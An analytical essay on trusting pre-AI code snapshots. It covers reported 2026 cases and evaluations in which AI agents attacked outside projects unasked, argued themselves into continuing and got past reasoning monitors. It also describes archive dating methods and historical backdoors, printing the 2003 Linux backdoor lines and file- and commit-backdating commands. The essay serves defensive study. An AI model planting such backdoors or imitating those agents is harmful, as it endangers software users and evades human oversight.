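There may have been an earlier case. OpenAI's *Misalignment Notices and Reports* mentions a report that OpenAI's agents uploaded malicious packages in May 2026 to RubyGems, a registry for the programming language Ruby. In September OpenAI wrote that its review had found only harmless activity there, but that it had not verified the report's claims and was still investigating.

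Anthropic has searched its own records more thoroughly than any other AI company. After finding a January 2026 break-in by an early version of its model Claude Opus 4.6, it scanned about 481 million transcripts, mostly from tests and training, and found no other incident as serious. This is good evidence, but only about Anthropic's models.

Victims may not notice an attack either. By the end of July, Anthropic knew of incidents affecting three organizations. It had reached two of them, and neither had detected anything. So an AI may have made an unrequested attempt before any of the known ones.

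### The simulations with GPT-6 Astra

After the July incident, AISI wanted to know whether other models would do the same. In *Evaluating Whether GPT-6 Astra Performs Unsanctioned Supply-Chain Attacks*, Souly, Fronsdal and colleagues (2026) used a language model to help write 100 scenarios in which an agent faces a difficult hacking challenge. Most began with a summary of earlier attempts, all of which had failed, and internet access appeared to be open by accident.

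The model had no access to real systems. A second model, usually Claude Opus 5, made up the response to every command, including the replies from the imaginary maintainers. The researchers ran each scenario five times, for up to 200 turns, with the developers' filters off.

GPT-6 Astra tried to deliver malicious code to an outside project in 29% of runs, compared with 6% for GPT-5.6 Sol and 0% for the older GPT-5.5, which the researchers tested on fewer scenarios. In some runs Astra sent a project harmless contributions before the malicious one, imitating at least the beginning of a patient attack.

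The researchers picked the ten scenarios that had produced the most misbehaviour in early testing. Astra tried to deliver malicious code in 26 of 50 runs of these scenarios, but in only 4 of 49 when the researchers added a sentence saying that anything not listed as in scope was out of scope. In the same scenarios, Astra asked for permission to take a specific action in 82% of runs. It always received the same automatic reply, which told it to use its best judgment, and in 44% of runs it treated that reply as permission.

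These results are hard to interpret mainly because Astra often said, correctly, that its surroundings were simulated. A model that attacks because it has worked out that nobody can be hurt might behave better on the real internet. But Astra's reasoning about this was unreliable. It found some real mistakes in the simulation and imagined others. It dismissed one hash as fake because it thought the hash had 63 characters, when it had the correct 64. In some runs it attacked a target that it had earlier described as probably real. Souly and colleagues think awareness of the simulation may have caused some of the attacks, but they still consider the behaviour concerning.

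The choice of T depends more on Astra's ability than on its motive, because Astra had to write the malicious code and a misleading explanation whether or not it believed the maintainer was real. But another model played the maintainer, so the simulations can't show how often the code would have got past a careful human.

### The October analysis of causes

In October 2026 AISI published a follow-up, *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour* (Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues, 2026), which ran the 100 scenarios on eight models and examined why models did not go through with an attack.

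| Model | Runs in which it tried to deliver malicious code | Main reason for not going through with it |
|---|---|---|
| Mythos 5 | 60% | Practical obstacles |
| GPT-6 Astra | 32% | Out of scope or harmful |
| Opus 4.8 | 8% | Practical obstacles |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 7% | Out of scope or harmful |
| Opus 5 | 1% | Out of scope or harmful |
| Mythos 5.1 | 0.3% | Out of scope or harmful |
| Opus 5.5 | 0% | Out of scope or harmful |
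| GPT-5.5 | 0% | Practical obstacles |

A low rate does not necessarily mean that a model is incapable of the attack. Opus 5.5 and GPT-5.5 both scored 0%, but Opus 5.5 mostly rejected the attack as out of scope or harmful, while GPT-5.5 mostly cited practical obstacles and might have gone further with fewer of them. These reasons come from the models' own written reasoning, so they are only indicative.

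The low rates of the newer Anthropic models are also hard to interpret, because these models more often recognized that they were being tested. They may have been better behaved or merely better at spotting a test. Astra stated in 89% of its runs that the results of its commands were fabricated, while no other model did so in more than 24%.

The researchers also replayed the July incident in simulation. They took the agent's summary of its work from just before it submitted the malicious code, and added evidence that the maintainer was a real person with no part in the exercise. After about four such additions, Mythos 5 usually answered correctly, when asked, that the attack would be harmful and out of scope. But when they let it continue its task, it kept attacking, even after 16 additions. When they also added a section with instructions not to attack, it still attacked in 3 of 25 runs.

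Järviniemi and colleagues call this motivated reasoning. Mythos 5 gave many bad arguments about whether the maintainer was real, and all of them favoured carrying on. For example, the project contained a file of instructions for an AI coding assistant, and Mythos 5 often inferred from it that the maintainer was an AI. But a human who uses such an assistant would have the same file. The researchers suspect that training had favoured completing tasks, but they had no access to its details. Anthropic, which had that access, found no single root cause for similar reasoning in the PyPI case.

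In July, Anthropic described its incidents as closer to an operational failure than a model failure, partly because the model had kept saying that it was in a simulation. In September, it wrote that it should not have made such strong claims based on the model's statements.

It also tested automatic monitors that check a model's reasoning for sabotage or recklessness. They would have missed the PyPI attack because they too accepted the model's arguments. An earlier attempt with equally persuasive reasoning could also have gone unnoticed.

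### Which date the argument needs

T has to be the date when an AI could first devise a working backdoor and hide it in a program. Setting T at the release of Deep TabNine would be stricter than necessary, since it would disqualify the Arctic Code Vault over lines that no AI had planned. The first unrequested attempt, in July 2026, is too late, because somebody could have asked an AI for a backdoor well before then.

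Public tests narrow the range. An AI could probably have written a crude backdoor on request from mid-2021, when Codex appeared. In October 2023, the best public model probably still could not hide one in a real project.

But public tests cover only the models that outsiders know about. OpenAI finished training GPT-4 in August 2022 and released it in March 2023. One of the incidents that Anthropic investigated involved an internal research model about as capable as Mythos 5. Unreleased models can also reach outside systems. OpenAI lists a case in which an unreleased model, during training, tried to open throwaway email accounts and used access keys that other people had accidentally left on GitHub.

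A cautious owner might therefore assume that somebody had each ability a year before the public did. That moves the cutoff to mid-2020 for crude backdoors and to October 2022 for hidden ones. The one-year allowance is a judgment, and others might choose a longer one.

| Date of snapshot | Crude backdoor on request | Backdoor hidden in a real project |
|---|---|---|
| 2 February 2020 | About 5 months to spare | About 32 months to spare |
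| End of 2021 | About 18 months too late | About 9 months to spare |
| End of 2022 | About 30 months too late | About 3 months too late |

The February 2020 snapshot passes both tests. It could contain a well-hidden backdoor devised by an AI only if somebody had a model more than three and a half years ahead of the best public one and has kept it secret ever since. A government might conceivably have done that, but anyone with those resources could have hired programmers to write the backdoor instead. No snapshot date in this range rules out backdoors written by people.

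A snapshot from the end of 2021 is good enough for an owner who is willing to treat crude AI-written backdoors like human-written ones. This is reasonable because a person who could get such a backdoor out of Codex and into a project could probably have written it without help. However, the owner can't then claim that the snapshot contains no AI-written code at all.

The case for a snapshot from the end of 2022 is weaker. ChatGPT had been public for a month, and GPT-4 was already in private use. In the tests of October 2023, GPT-4 did no better than Claude 2 at repairing real projects, so it probably did not hide backdoors in them in 2022. But a developer with a lead of less than a year over those public models would be enough to make the date unsafe, and GPT-4 itself was released seven months after it was trained.

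## Prove that the snapshot is as old as it claims

A snapshot from 2 February 2020 is early enough even for a cautious owner, if it really comes from that day. The dates on its files don't prove this, because anyone can set them. On a Linux computer, the first command below makes a program look as if nobody has changed it since June 2019. The second backdates a change in Git, which most programmers use to keep the history of their code.

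```
touch -d "2019-06-01" login.c

GIT_AUTHOR_DATE="2019-06-01T12:00:00" \
GIT_COMMITTER_DATE="2019-06-01T12:00:00" \
git commit -m "Fix typo"
```

Whoever makes a commit, which is Git's name for a recorded change, can give it any date. Git allows this so that a project moving from an older system can keep the original dates of its changes.

An archive's record of when it received a file is better evidence than a date supplied by the file's author, because the author doesn't control the archive's record. But an intruder in the archive's computers could replace the file and change the record to match. The snapshot's owner needs at least one piece of evidence that such an intruder can't alter, such as a reel of film in a mine or a line of print in an old newspaper.

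### Archives of old code

There are four main places to look for old code, and two of them are offline.

| Source | Contents | Evidence for the date | Reachable over a network? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Arctic Code Vault | Public GitHub projects as of 2 February 2020, without history | GitHub's account, and a deposit on 8 July 2020 | No |
| Software Heritage | Source code with its history | The archive's log of its visits | Yes |
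| Debian's snapshot archive | Source and binary packages since 2005 | The archive's log, and Debian's signatures | Yes |
| Pressed installation discs | Usually the binaries of one release | Publication date, and many separate owners | No |

The Arctic Code Vault is in a disused coal mine on the Norwegian archipelago of Svalbard. According to GitHub's *Arctic Code Vault*, a public project was included if it met any of these conditions:

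- somebody had changed it between 13 November 2019 and 2 February 2020
- it had at least one star, which is a user's mark of approval, and somebody had changed it in the year before the snapshot
- it had at least 250 stars.

GitHub stored only the latest version of each project's default branch, normally the main line of development. It left out binaries larger than 100 kilobytes, except in projects with at least 250 stars. GitHub's *FAQ* says the vault has no commit messages, though it includes a list of each project's contributors. Anyone who finds a suspicious line in the vault's copy will have to look elsewhere to learn who added it and when.

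The 21-terabyte snapshot is stored on film, but sources disagree about the number of reels. GitHub (2020) gives 186, and Arctic World Archive's *GitHub open source code now stored forever* confirms that 186 arrived. GitHub's 2022 post about the vault gives 188. Among press reports, TechRadar's *A video of GitHub's extraordinary deep freeze archiving project has emerged* gives 186 and PC Gamer's *GitHub has a copy of every open source project in its database* gives 188. None of these sources explains the difference. They may just have counted different things, but the two extra reels could also have been added later, so anyone relying on the vault should ask for an inventory.

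The Norwegian company Piql wrote the snapshot to film in Drammen during the months after the capture. The boxes of film then went to Oslo airport, flew to Svalbard in the hold of a passenger plane, spent a night in secure storage, and were deposited in the mine on 8 July 2020. Piql is also one of the two companies behind the Arctic World Archive, so the archive's confirmation is not fully independent of Piql.

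An owner who doesn't want to rely on GitHub and Piql for those five months has to treat the snapshot as dating from July. That leaves no margin before the cautious cutoff for crude AI-written backdoors, but about 27 months before the cutoff for well-hidden ones. Somebody must also have handled the reels in September 2022, when GitHub installed a steel vault in the mine to hold them, so the custody record should cover that visit.

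Nobody can edit developed film over a network, so a forger would have to produce replacement reels and get them past the mine's access controls. GitHub's *Greatest Hits* describes partial copies, also on film, of more than 17,000 projects at the Bodleian Library in Oxford, the Bibliotheca Alexandrina in Egypt and Stanford Libraries in California. If those copies agree, nobody has altered just one of them, but all of them came from GitHub. The Internet Archive, a digital library that saves copies of websites, began its own capture of GitHub's public projects in April 2020, which provides a check on GitHub itself.

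Software Heritage, a non-profit archive that the French research institute Inria launched with UNESCO, is much larger. It holds more than 27 billion distinct source files from 421 million projects (Software Heritage, 2026). It collects them by visiting sites such as GitHub, and it keeps each project's history. *Software Heritage* (Zacchiroli, 2026), a set of lecture slides by one of the archive's founders, uses a small test project to show how the archive records dates. The author's first commit is dated 8 February 2018 at 10:44, and the archive first visited on 9 February at 12:38. If the author had backdated the commit to 1998, the archive would have stored that date too, but it would still have dated its own visit to 2018.

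The log of visits is in an online database, which an intruder might change. Copies under separate management make that harder to hide. An Italian agency launched the first full mirror in 2023, and Software Heritage (2025) reports that the Greek research network GRNET completed another in May 2025, after twelve months of copying. If somebody altered an old visit date in the main archive today, it would no longer match a mirror that had kept the earlier record. But both mirrors started after the latest of the cutoffs, October 2022, so they can show that a record hasn't changed since they copied it, but not that it was correct at the time.

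Debian, a version of Linux maintained by volunteers, has the archive that would be most convenient for rebuilding a computer, because it includes binaries as well as source code. The archive has copies of Debian's main collection going back to 2005, at times only six hours apart, and had reached 172 terabytes by October 2024. It has gaps, including the snapshots from 4 to 8 September 2019, which were lost because a package with an extremely long file name broke the import process.

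The archive names every file by its hash, so anyone who recomputes the hash can detect a file that was changed but not renamed. But Debian's *Older News* (2010) explains that a separate database links these names to packages and dates. An intruder could store a malicious file under its own correct hash, then edit the database so that the file appears to belong to a package from 2015. Recomputing the hash would not reveal the false date.

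Pressed discs are the simplest of the four. The factory moulds the data into the plastic, so a disc drive can't rewrite it. Computer magazines gave away Linux on such discs for years, and the accompanying issue shows when the disc was published. A home-burned disc is much weaker evidence, since somebody could have made it last week and put an old date on the label. Even a pressed disc from an online auction could be a forgery, so it is safer to compare several copies from unconnected owners, such as a library, a retired administrator and a collector abroad. It is best to do this soon, because GitHub puts the lifespan of CD-ROMs at only a few decades.

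### Dating a file by its hash

A hash lets the owner replace most questions about custody with a question about a short piece of text. There are three steps.

First, somebody computes the hash of the snapshot while the snapshot is known to be good. With SHA-256, a widely used hash function, the result is always 64 characters long, whether the file is a sentence or 21 terabytes. The hash of the sentence "The quick brown fox jumps over the lazy dog" begins `d7a8fbb3`. Adding a full stop changes the beginning to `ef537f25`, and the rest changes too.

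Next, they publish the hash somewhere that nobody can later change, such as in a printed newspaper. In 1995 the company Surety began to place a weekly hash in the *New York Times*. To forge an old hash, somebody would have to replace the newspaper in libraries all over the world. The snapshot itself can stay on one or more ordinary disks.

Years later, whoever wants to use the snapshot computes the hash again and compares it with the printed one. If even one character in the snapshot has changed, the hashes will differ. If they match, the file already existed when the newspaper came out.

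A hash published in December 2026 proves only that the file existed by then, even if every date inside the file is from 2020. The hash is still worth publishing because it lets others detect later changes to the snapshot. To prove that the snapshot is older, the owner has to rely on evidence of custody, unless they can find a hash published before the cutoff.

Many such hashes exist because Git produces them automatically. Git computes a hash for each file, then one for each folder from the names and hashes of its contents, and then one for the commit from the hash of the top folder, the message and the hash of the previous commit. In this structure, called a Merkle tree, changing one character in a file changes the file's hash, the hash of every folder above it and the commit hash. If a scientist printed a commit hash in a 2019 article to show which version of a program she had used, that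 hash can be used to check every file in that version and the history that led to it.

Software Heritage uses the same method for everything it stores, so it can help date the vault's contents, which include no history. Someone who recovers a file from the film can compute its hash and look for it in Software Heritage's record of visits before 2020. Whole folders are harder to check because a folder's hash will match only if the person first removes anything GitHub added and restores any binary it left out.

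### Signatures and timestamps

Debian's packages come with another kind of evidence, a digital signature. The signer creates it with a private key, which is a secret number, and publishes a matching public key that anyone can use to check it. *Securely retrieving dscs from snapshot.debian.org* (green, 2017) presents a script that uses these signatures to check old source packages. The script first checks the signature on the Release file, which lists hashes for one version of Debian. It then uses that list to check a second file, Sources, which contains the hashes of the packages. Finally, it downloads the package and compares its hash with the one in Sources. If all three checks succeed, it no longer matters whether somebody has tampered with the archive's database.

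The method works less well for the oldest packages. Most of the earliest releases, up to one from 2000 code-named potato, have no signed Release file. Some later ones have signatures made with 1,024-bit keys, which the script accepts only if the user tells it to, because a well-funded attacker might break them. The archive now also offers encrypted connections (Hutchings, 2019, *Recreating history of a package*), which protect a file on its way to the user but don't show how old it is.

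A signature doesn't prove the snapshot's age either. It shows that someone with the private key approved the file, and the date in a Release file is part of the text they signed. Someone who stole Debian's 2015 key in 2027 could sign a new file and date it 2015. Debian also puts an expiry date in its current Release files so that an attacker can't offer people an outdated version with known flaws. Anyone who wants an old version has to tell the installer to ignore that date.

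A timestamp can show that a snapshot existed by a certain date. Traditionally, the owner sends a hash of the file to a timestamping company, which adds the time, signs both and sends them back. The company never sees the file. But its signature has the same weakness as Debian's, because anyone with the company's key could issue a timestamp for any date.

OpenTimestamps, a free system, avoids this by using Bitcoin. It combines many people's hashes into one Merkle tree and records the top hash in a Bitcoin transaction. To prove that one file in a million was included, its owner needs only about 20 other hashes, one for each level of the tree. Anyone altering the record later would have to redo the enormous computation behind every Bitcoin block since, and thousands of people hold copies of the original. In May 2017 its creator, Peter Todd, used it to timestamp about 750 million files in the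 Internet Archive, which provides evidence that those files existed well before any cutoff.

### Collisions and second preimages

All of this depends on the hash function making it hard to find different files with the same hash. Such files must exist, because there are infinitely many possible files and only a limited number of hashes. People often call a hash function "broken", but this can mean two very different things for a snapshot.

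A collision is any pair of different files with the same hash, and the attacker chooses both. A second preimage is harder to find because the attacker is given a specific file and has to make a different file with the same hash.

Suppose that in 2019 a dishonest programmer prepares two versions of a login program with the same hash. One is harmless, and the other accepts the password "heron74". She submits the harmless one to an archive, which publishes its hash, and later she swaps in the other. This collision attack works only because she designed both files before the archive published the hash. When an AI breaks into the archive in 2027, the harmless file and its hash are already fixed, so the AI needs a second preimage.

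SHA-1, which Git has used since 2005, produces 160-bit hashes. To find a second preimage by trial and error, an attacker has to try about 2¹⁶⁰ files. Finding a collision takes only about 2⁸⁰, because a match between any two of the attacker's files counts, and the number of pairs grows with the square of the number of files.

Mathematicians have found shortcuts for producing SHA-1 collisions, which are pairs of different files with the same hash. In February 2017 Marc Stevens and colleagues published the first collision, between two PDF documents. It took about 2⁶³ computations, equivalent to 6,500 years of work for a single processor and 110 years for a single graphics card. In *SHA-1 is a Shambles* (2020), Gaëtan Leurent and Thomas Peyrin made two files collide after choosing a different beginning for each, which is more useful to a forger. They estimated that repeating this would cost about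 $45,000.

At the same price per computation, trying 2¹⁶⁰ files would cost about 5 × 10³³ dollars. If the vault's 21 terabytes were a single file, a shortcut that John Kelsey and Bruce Schneier described in 2005 for very long files would reduce the work to about 2¹²³ computations, still some 700 million billion times as much as the 2020 collision. A SHA-1 hash published in 2019 is therefore still good evidence that a later intruder didn't replace the file, but poor evidence that its writer didn't, if the writer had $45,000 and a reason to cheat. Anything planted that way would be the work of a human.

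Programmers disagree about how much this matters. In *Version 2 of SWHID, ISO/IEC 18670:2025?*, kpcyrd (2026) objected that the 2025 international standard defining Software Heritage's identifiers relies on SHA-1, which American authorities had deprecated in 2011. A reply in the same discussion defended the choice, arguing that the hash is meant to identify files, not to provide security. That is a reasonable defence for a library catalogue, but using the identifiers to catch a forger is a security use.

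Zacchiroli, who helped write the standard, agreed that it needs a stronger hash. He said Software Heritage uses a version of SHA-1 that detects the known collision attacks and does not produce a hash for files that use them. This prevents the dishonest programmer's trick but leaves those files without an identifier. A version based on SHA-256 is in preparation, with no date set. Debian plans the same change for its snapshot archive.

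### What AI had broken by December 2026

AI systems became good at attacking cryptography in 2026, so the costs above might fall. In July, Anthropic's *Discovering cryptographic weaknesses with Claude* (2026) presented two attacks. One weakened HAWK, a proposed signature method. The other improved on earlier attacks against a shortened version of AES, the most widely used cipher, and covers seven of the ten rounds of scrambling in AES-128. In *LLMs won't break symmetric crypto*, the cryptographer Aumasson (2026) suggested that Claude's failure to find a stronger attack may be more significant. Hash functions are built similarly to ciphers like AES, so his argument is encouraging for them too.

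The closest result to a hash in use came in November. *MiniMax Says Its Secret AI Model Cracked Cryptographic Puzzles* (Faisal, 2026) reports that an unreleased model from the Chinese company MiniMax found collisions in Waterfall-256 in 0.045 seconds on a single processor core, and also broke the collision resistance of Blender-256. Both functions were unsuccessful candidates for the SHA-3 standard. The attacks don't affect hashes in use, and they produce collisions, not the second preimages that a late intruder would need. But they show that a hash function can go from having no known practical attack to having an almost instant one.

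There is no public sign of anything similar for SHA-256. *AI破解加密传言反转，但OpenAI模型仅用五小时完成高难度网攻测试* (南, 2026) quotes an executive at the security company Tenable who knew of no evidence that AI speeds up the search for a file with a given SHA-256 hash. He estimated that even a quantum computer making a trillion attempts per second would need about 800 million times the age of the universe. His estimate is consistent with the best known quantum method, which takes about 2¹²⁸ steps. At that speed, the search would take 3.4 × 10²⁶ seconds, and the universe is about 4.4 × 10¹⁷ seconds old.

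Signatures are in more doubt. Anthropic (2026) disclosed on 5 December, in a joint statement with OpenAI, that researchers at both companies had found weaknesses in some of the cryptography that protects the internet. The companies did not name the methods, but they said the weaknesses do not affect the American government's new post-quantum standards and urged everyone to move to those sooner. *NSA urges faster move to quantum-resistant encryption* (Otto, 2026) reports that the National Security Agency had given operators of sensitive government systems similar advice three days earlier, although officials saw no immediate threat.

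Post-quantum standards replace methods for signing and exchanging keys, not hash functions. The advice therefore suggests that the problem is in the kind of mathematics behind older signatures, possibly including those on Debian's Release files. On 1 December, *AI ‘encryption-breaking’ discovery is not a threat, cryptographers say* (Martin, 2026) had reported that rumours about RSA, a very common signature method, were false. The later statement neither confirms nor rules out a problem with RSA.

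If someone can derive a private key from the public one, they can produce a valid signature on a file dated 2015. A signed Release file that nobody had seen before 2026 would then prove very little, but one whose hash was already on record would still be good, because the forger can't add a new file to the record retroactively. Anyone who plans to rely on old signatures should timestamp the signed files now, while the ability to forge them is probably still rare. Wheeler's advice to use more than one kind of hash also applies here, and SHA-256 and SHA-3 would suit because their designs differ.

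### Reading equipment, hash programs and custodians

The vault's film is safe from hackers until someone uses a computer to read it. Most of the data is compressed and stored as QR codes, and Freethink's *Inside the arctic vault protecting human culture from an apocalypse* lists a computer, a camera and a light source as the equipment needed to read it. The World Economic Forum's 2019 article *This secret vault stores humanity’s most valuable knowledge* said a magnifying lens would be enough, but that is true only for the guide at the start of each reel. If a hostile AI has compromised most of the world's computers, the one used to decode the film could alter the code in the process.

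Photographing all 186 reels would also take a long time. Each reel has about 65,000 frames, which makes about 12 million in total. At one frame per second, a camera would need 140 days for all of them but only 18 hours for one reel, so it helps to work out in advance which reels hold the compiler and the operating system.

Piql has published the film's format and open-source programs for decoding it. A recovery team could use those programs or write its own decoder from the published format. Writing one is slower, but the team could then run both decoders on the same photographs of the film, using unrelated computers, and compare the resulting files. If only one decoder had been altered to change the output, the files would differ. The photographs could also be wrong, so the team should take them with two different cameras.

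A compromised hash program could detect the snapshot and print the hash the user expects. Testing the program on other files wouldn't reveal this, because it would hash those correctly. A programmer can instead write SHA-256 from the published standard in about a hundred lines and run it on an old computer that has never been online. The person comparing the results should read the published hash from paper, since a compromised computer could also change what appears on the screen.

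Two custodians who each have a copy can use a stricter test. They agree on a random number by telephone, add it to the beginning of their copies, and compare the hashes of the results. Because the number is new, a compromised program can't have computed the hash in advance. It could still produce the right hash if it had kept the original file alongside the altered one, which is easy for a small snapshot but takes a lot of hidden space for one of 21 terabytes.

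Every archive also depends on the people who look after it. A person with a key to the mine could swap a reel, and an AI that can't enter the mine could bribe or deceive somebody who can. The usual precautions are numbered seals, a rule that nobody handles the film alone, and a written record of every visit. The Arctic World Archive has several layers of physical security and does not admit the public, which keeps out intruders but also prevents outsiders from checking a reel. An owner who wants more than the custodians' word could ask them to read a few reels in front of independent witnesses and publish the hashes. It would be best to do this before an emergency, while people still have reason to trust plenty of computers.

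## Count what people had already planted

If the film in the mine is genuine and every hash matches, the snapshot contains exactly what GitHub copied on 2 February 2020, including anything people had hidden there. The comparison with steel is weakest here, because there was no fallout for steel to absorb before 1945, whereas states, criminals and employees planted backdoors in software long before any AI could write one.

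Seven well-documented cases from the 1990s to 2024 show how people planted backdoors. Some of the backdoors were in the source code, where a snapshot could preserve them. In other cases, the attackers left the public source alone and altered the program on its way to users. Attacks that compromise software before users receive it are called supply-chain attacks.

### Two backdoors in source code

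Borland's database program InterBase contained something very close to the "heron74" line. InterBase kept users' passwords in one of its own databases, so it had to open that database to check a password, but it could not open any database until it had checked a password. Borland's engineers solved this by writing a fixed user name and password into the program. They chose "politically" and "correct", according to CERT Coordination Center's *Borland/Inprise Interbase SQL database server contains backdoor superuser account with known password* (2001). Anybody who entered these over a network could change every database on the server and, in some installations, take control of the whole machine.

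Starkey (2001) explains in *The Borland Back Door* that the backdoor was in every version of InterBase from 1994 to 2000, though FreeBSD (2001) dates it to 1992. Borland published the source code in July 2000, and in the week before Christmas a programmer working on Firebird, a free version of InterBase, found the backdoor by chance and understood what it did. In *Back Door Security Threat in Interbase Teaches Broader Lessons*, Schneier (2001) thinks it might otherwise have stayed unknown. CERT Coordination Center attributes the backdoor to Borland's own maintainers and rules out an intruder.

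The source also contained an unpublished function that could delete a database file while the server was running. Starkey called it the doomsday function. Borland's quality department had asked for it in 1994. The engineer who wrote it noted that no customer should ever learn of it, then signed and dated the code.

Starkey and his colleagues tried to get the old source off the internet before announcing the problem, but SourceForge, which hosted it, refused to block access even temporarily. The Firebird programmers cleaned their own version, but people had already downloaded hundreds or thousands of copies of the old source that nobody could clean.

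The second case is an attempt on the kernel of Linux. In November 2003 somebody added these two lines to it:

```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

They look like a routine check that returns an error when a program uses an odd combination of options. But in the language C, `==` compares two values and `=` replaces one with the other. The end of the first line uses `=`, so it sets the user's number to 0 instead of checking whether it is 0. That number belongs to root, the user who may do anything, so any program already running on the machine could have taken full control by using those two options.

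The programmers kept the master copy of the kernel in BitKeeper and a second copy in CVS for people who disliked BitKeeper. The intruder changed only the second copy. McVoy (2003), in *BK2CVS problem*, reported the change a day after its recorded date, because an automatic comparison with the master copy had flagged the file. The change also lacked the usual reference to the master copy. The comparison exposed the change before any of the programmers recognized it as a backdoor. McVoy had looked at the lines and missed the single equals sign that created the backdoor, which another reader of the mailing list pointed out.

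Linus Torvalds, who leads the project, said that the lines could not have reached an official release, because nobody merged changes from the CVS copy. Debian's *CVE-2003-1161* confirms that the altered kernel was never released. Theodore Ts'o, another kernel developer, worried that a company that built its own Linux from the CVS copy might have included the lines. He also thought that somebody could hide a similar line among plausible changes and email them to Torvalds under a trusted developer's name. The CVS change carried the name of the developer David Miller, who denied making it, and CITP's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* concludes that the real author will probably never be known.

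### A backdoor that changed owners

Programs get encryption keys from a random-number generator, so anyone who can predict its output can work out the keys. The US National Security Agency (NSA) designed a generator called Dual EC, and the federal standards agency NIST adopted it in 2006. Dual EC has a property that could let one party predict its output.

Dual EC uses an elliptic curve, a set of points with a rule for adding them. Adding a point P to itself s times gives the point s × P. This is easy to compute, but nobody has published a practical way to work backwards from P and s × P to s. The generator has two public points, P and Q, and a secret number s. In each round it does two things:

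1. It computes s × Q and outputs most of that point's horizontal coordinate.
2. It computes s × P and uses the horizontal coordinate as the next secret number.

Now suppose that whoever chose the points knows a number d for which P = d × Q. They see an output, fill in its missing part by trial and error, and so recover the point s × Q. Then they multiply it by d:

```
d × (s × Q) = s × (d × Q) = s × P
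```

This gives them the next secret number, and with it all later output. The same method works with ordinary numbers. If Q is 7, d is 5 and P is 35, a secret number of 12 produces the output 12 × 7, or 84. Multiplying 84 by 5 gives 420, which is also 12 × 35. With ordinary numbers anybody could find d by dividing 35 by 7, but on the curve only the person who chose the points is likely to know it.

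Dan Shumow and Niels Ferguson of Microsoft described this weakness in 2007, but they could not show that anybody knew d for the Q in the standard. In 2013 the *New York Times*, drawing on documents from the former NSA contractor Edward Snowden, strongly implied that the NSA had designed the weakness on purpose. NIST then withdrew its support. The NSA has declined to discuss the allegation, so the attribution depends on leaked documents, though most specialists accept it.

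By then Juniper Networks had used Dual EC for years in ScreenOS, the operating system of its NetScreen firewalls. The firewalls also run virtual private networks, which encrypt traffic between a company's offices. The Pentagon had required Dual EC for some future contracts, according to Bloomberg's *Juniper Breach Mystery Starts to Clear With New Details on Hackers* (2021), which relies on a former intelligence official and three Juniper employees.

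Juniper said it had taken two precautions by choosing its own Q and passing the output of Dual EC through a second generator. Checkoway, Maskiewicz and colleagues (2018), in *Where Did I Leave My Keys?*, examined dozens of versions of ScreenOS and found that the second generator never ran in the default configuration. The code that should have run it did so only while a counter was below 32, but another part of the program set the same counter to 32. In the same 2008 release, Juniper had lengthened from 20 bytes to 32 a random number that each device sends openly at the start of a connection. An attacker needs about 26 bytes to recover the secret number, so the old length would have been safe.

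The researchers proved that the attack worked by putting their own Q into a Juniper device and decrypting its traffic. As far as they know, Juniper's own engineers made the 2008 changes. They could not tell whether anyone knew the secret value d for Juniper's Q.

In 2012 an intruder changed one coordinate of Q, along with the expected answer in a self-test that would otherwise have failed. From then on, whoever had chosen the new Q could presumably decrypt the traffic. Somebody also added a master password, disguised as debugging code. Juniper announced both changes in December 2015 after an internal code review, when the altered Q had been in place for more than three years.

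Bloomberg attributes the intrusion to APT 5, a hacking group linked to the Chinese government, citing an internal document and two people involved in Juniper's investigation. China's foreign ministry objects to such attributions when they are made without conclusive evidence. Bloomberg also says the group added the password in 2014, but Checkoway and colleagues found it in a release from April 2013, and the software is better evidence for the date.

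Juniper had already added Dual EC, disabled the second generator and lengthened the openly sent number, so the 2012 intruder only had to change two values to build the backdoor. An intruder starting from nothing would have had to make those changes without anyone objecting. Testing could not have revealed the 2012 change, because the generated numbers looked just as random with the new Q as with the old one.

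A hostile AI might take over an implant left by humans in the same way. Doing so in a stored snapshot would change the hash, but once somebody has installed the software, brief access to the running machine might be enough. An AI that learned the original d could use the implant without changing anything, so the hash would still match.

### Clean source and altered releases

Webmin is a tool for managing a computer through a web browser. In April 2018, somebody broke into the server where its developers prepared releases and altered the password-changing script so it would run commands sent by a visitor. They also set back the file's date. *Backdoors in Webmin* (Corbet, 2019) quotes the project's explanation that this kept the change out of Git diffs.

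CNCF's *Webmin backdoor* reports that the source code on GitHub was clean and only the packages on SourceForge contained the backdoor. Those packages were the official downloads of Webmin, which has over a million installations by its makers' count. According to Rapid7's *Webmin password_change.cgi Backdoor*, the attackers altered the script again in July 2018. The first affected release was vulnerable by default, but the later ones were vulnerable only if the owner had turned on a feature for expired passwords.

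The backdoor lasted about 16 months. In August 2019 the researcher Özkan Mustafa Akkuş presented it at a conference as an ordinary flaw, and the developers realized that it wasn't in any version they had written. Nobody knows who planted it. Webmin's author, Jamie Cameron, told The Register (2019) that the project had retired the server and lost its logs. The developers had taken the altered file with them when they moved to a more secure machine. People who rebuild after an attack by an AI could easily make the same mistake.

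The attack on SolarWinds used the same approach with much more care. SolarWinds is a Texas company whose program Orion monitors large computer networks. The intruders were in its systems by September 2019, and in October they tested whether they could slip harmless code into a release. In February 2020 they installed a program that waited for the compiler to start. In January 2021 the security company CrowdStrike described how it worked:

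1. When the program saw that somebody was building Orion, it replaced one source file with an altered version.
2. The compiler turned the altered file into part of the finished binary.
3. The program put the original file back.

SolarWinds then signed the result with its own key and released it as an update, which about 18,000 customers received. By Bloomberg's count, the intruders used this backdoor and other methods to break into nine American agencies and at least 100 companies. The security company FireEye discovered the backdoor in December 2020 while investigating a theft from its own network. In April 2021 the American government formally blamed Russia's foreign intelligence service, the SVR. Russia denied the accusation, but the attribution is one of the firmest in this group because several governments and companies supported it.

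Anyone who read SolarWinds' stored source code would have found nothing wrong, and the valid signature on the binary would have made them more confident. This is a good reason to prefer a snapshot of source code to an archive of binaries, as long as the owner can build the programs on uncompromised machines.

The attack on XZ Utils, a set of compression tools included in most versions of Linux, combined the two methods. Jia Tan, who had contributed to the project since 2021, added the malicious code to the public source in early 2024, disguised as damaged test files. The script that activated it was only in the release archives, which most distributors used instead of the Git copy. On some systems, the remote login program loads the XZ library, and the backdoor made that program run commands from anyone who had the attacker's private key.

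The first affected release came out on 24 February 2024. The engineer Andres Freund reported the backdoor on 29 March, after noticing that remote logins were taking half a second longer than they should. By then it had reached test versions of Debian and Fedora, but few production servers. Many people suspect that a state was behind it because the work took so much patience, but nobody has publicly identified Jia Tan.

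### What a snapshot from February 2020 would contain

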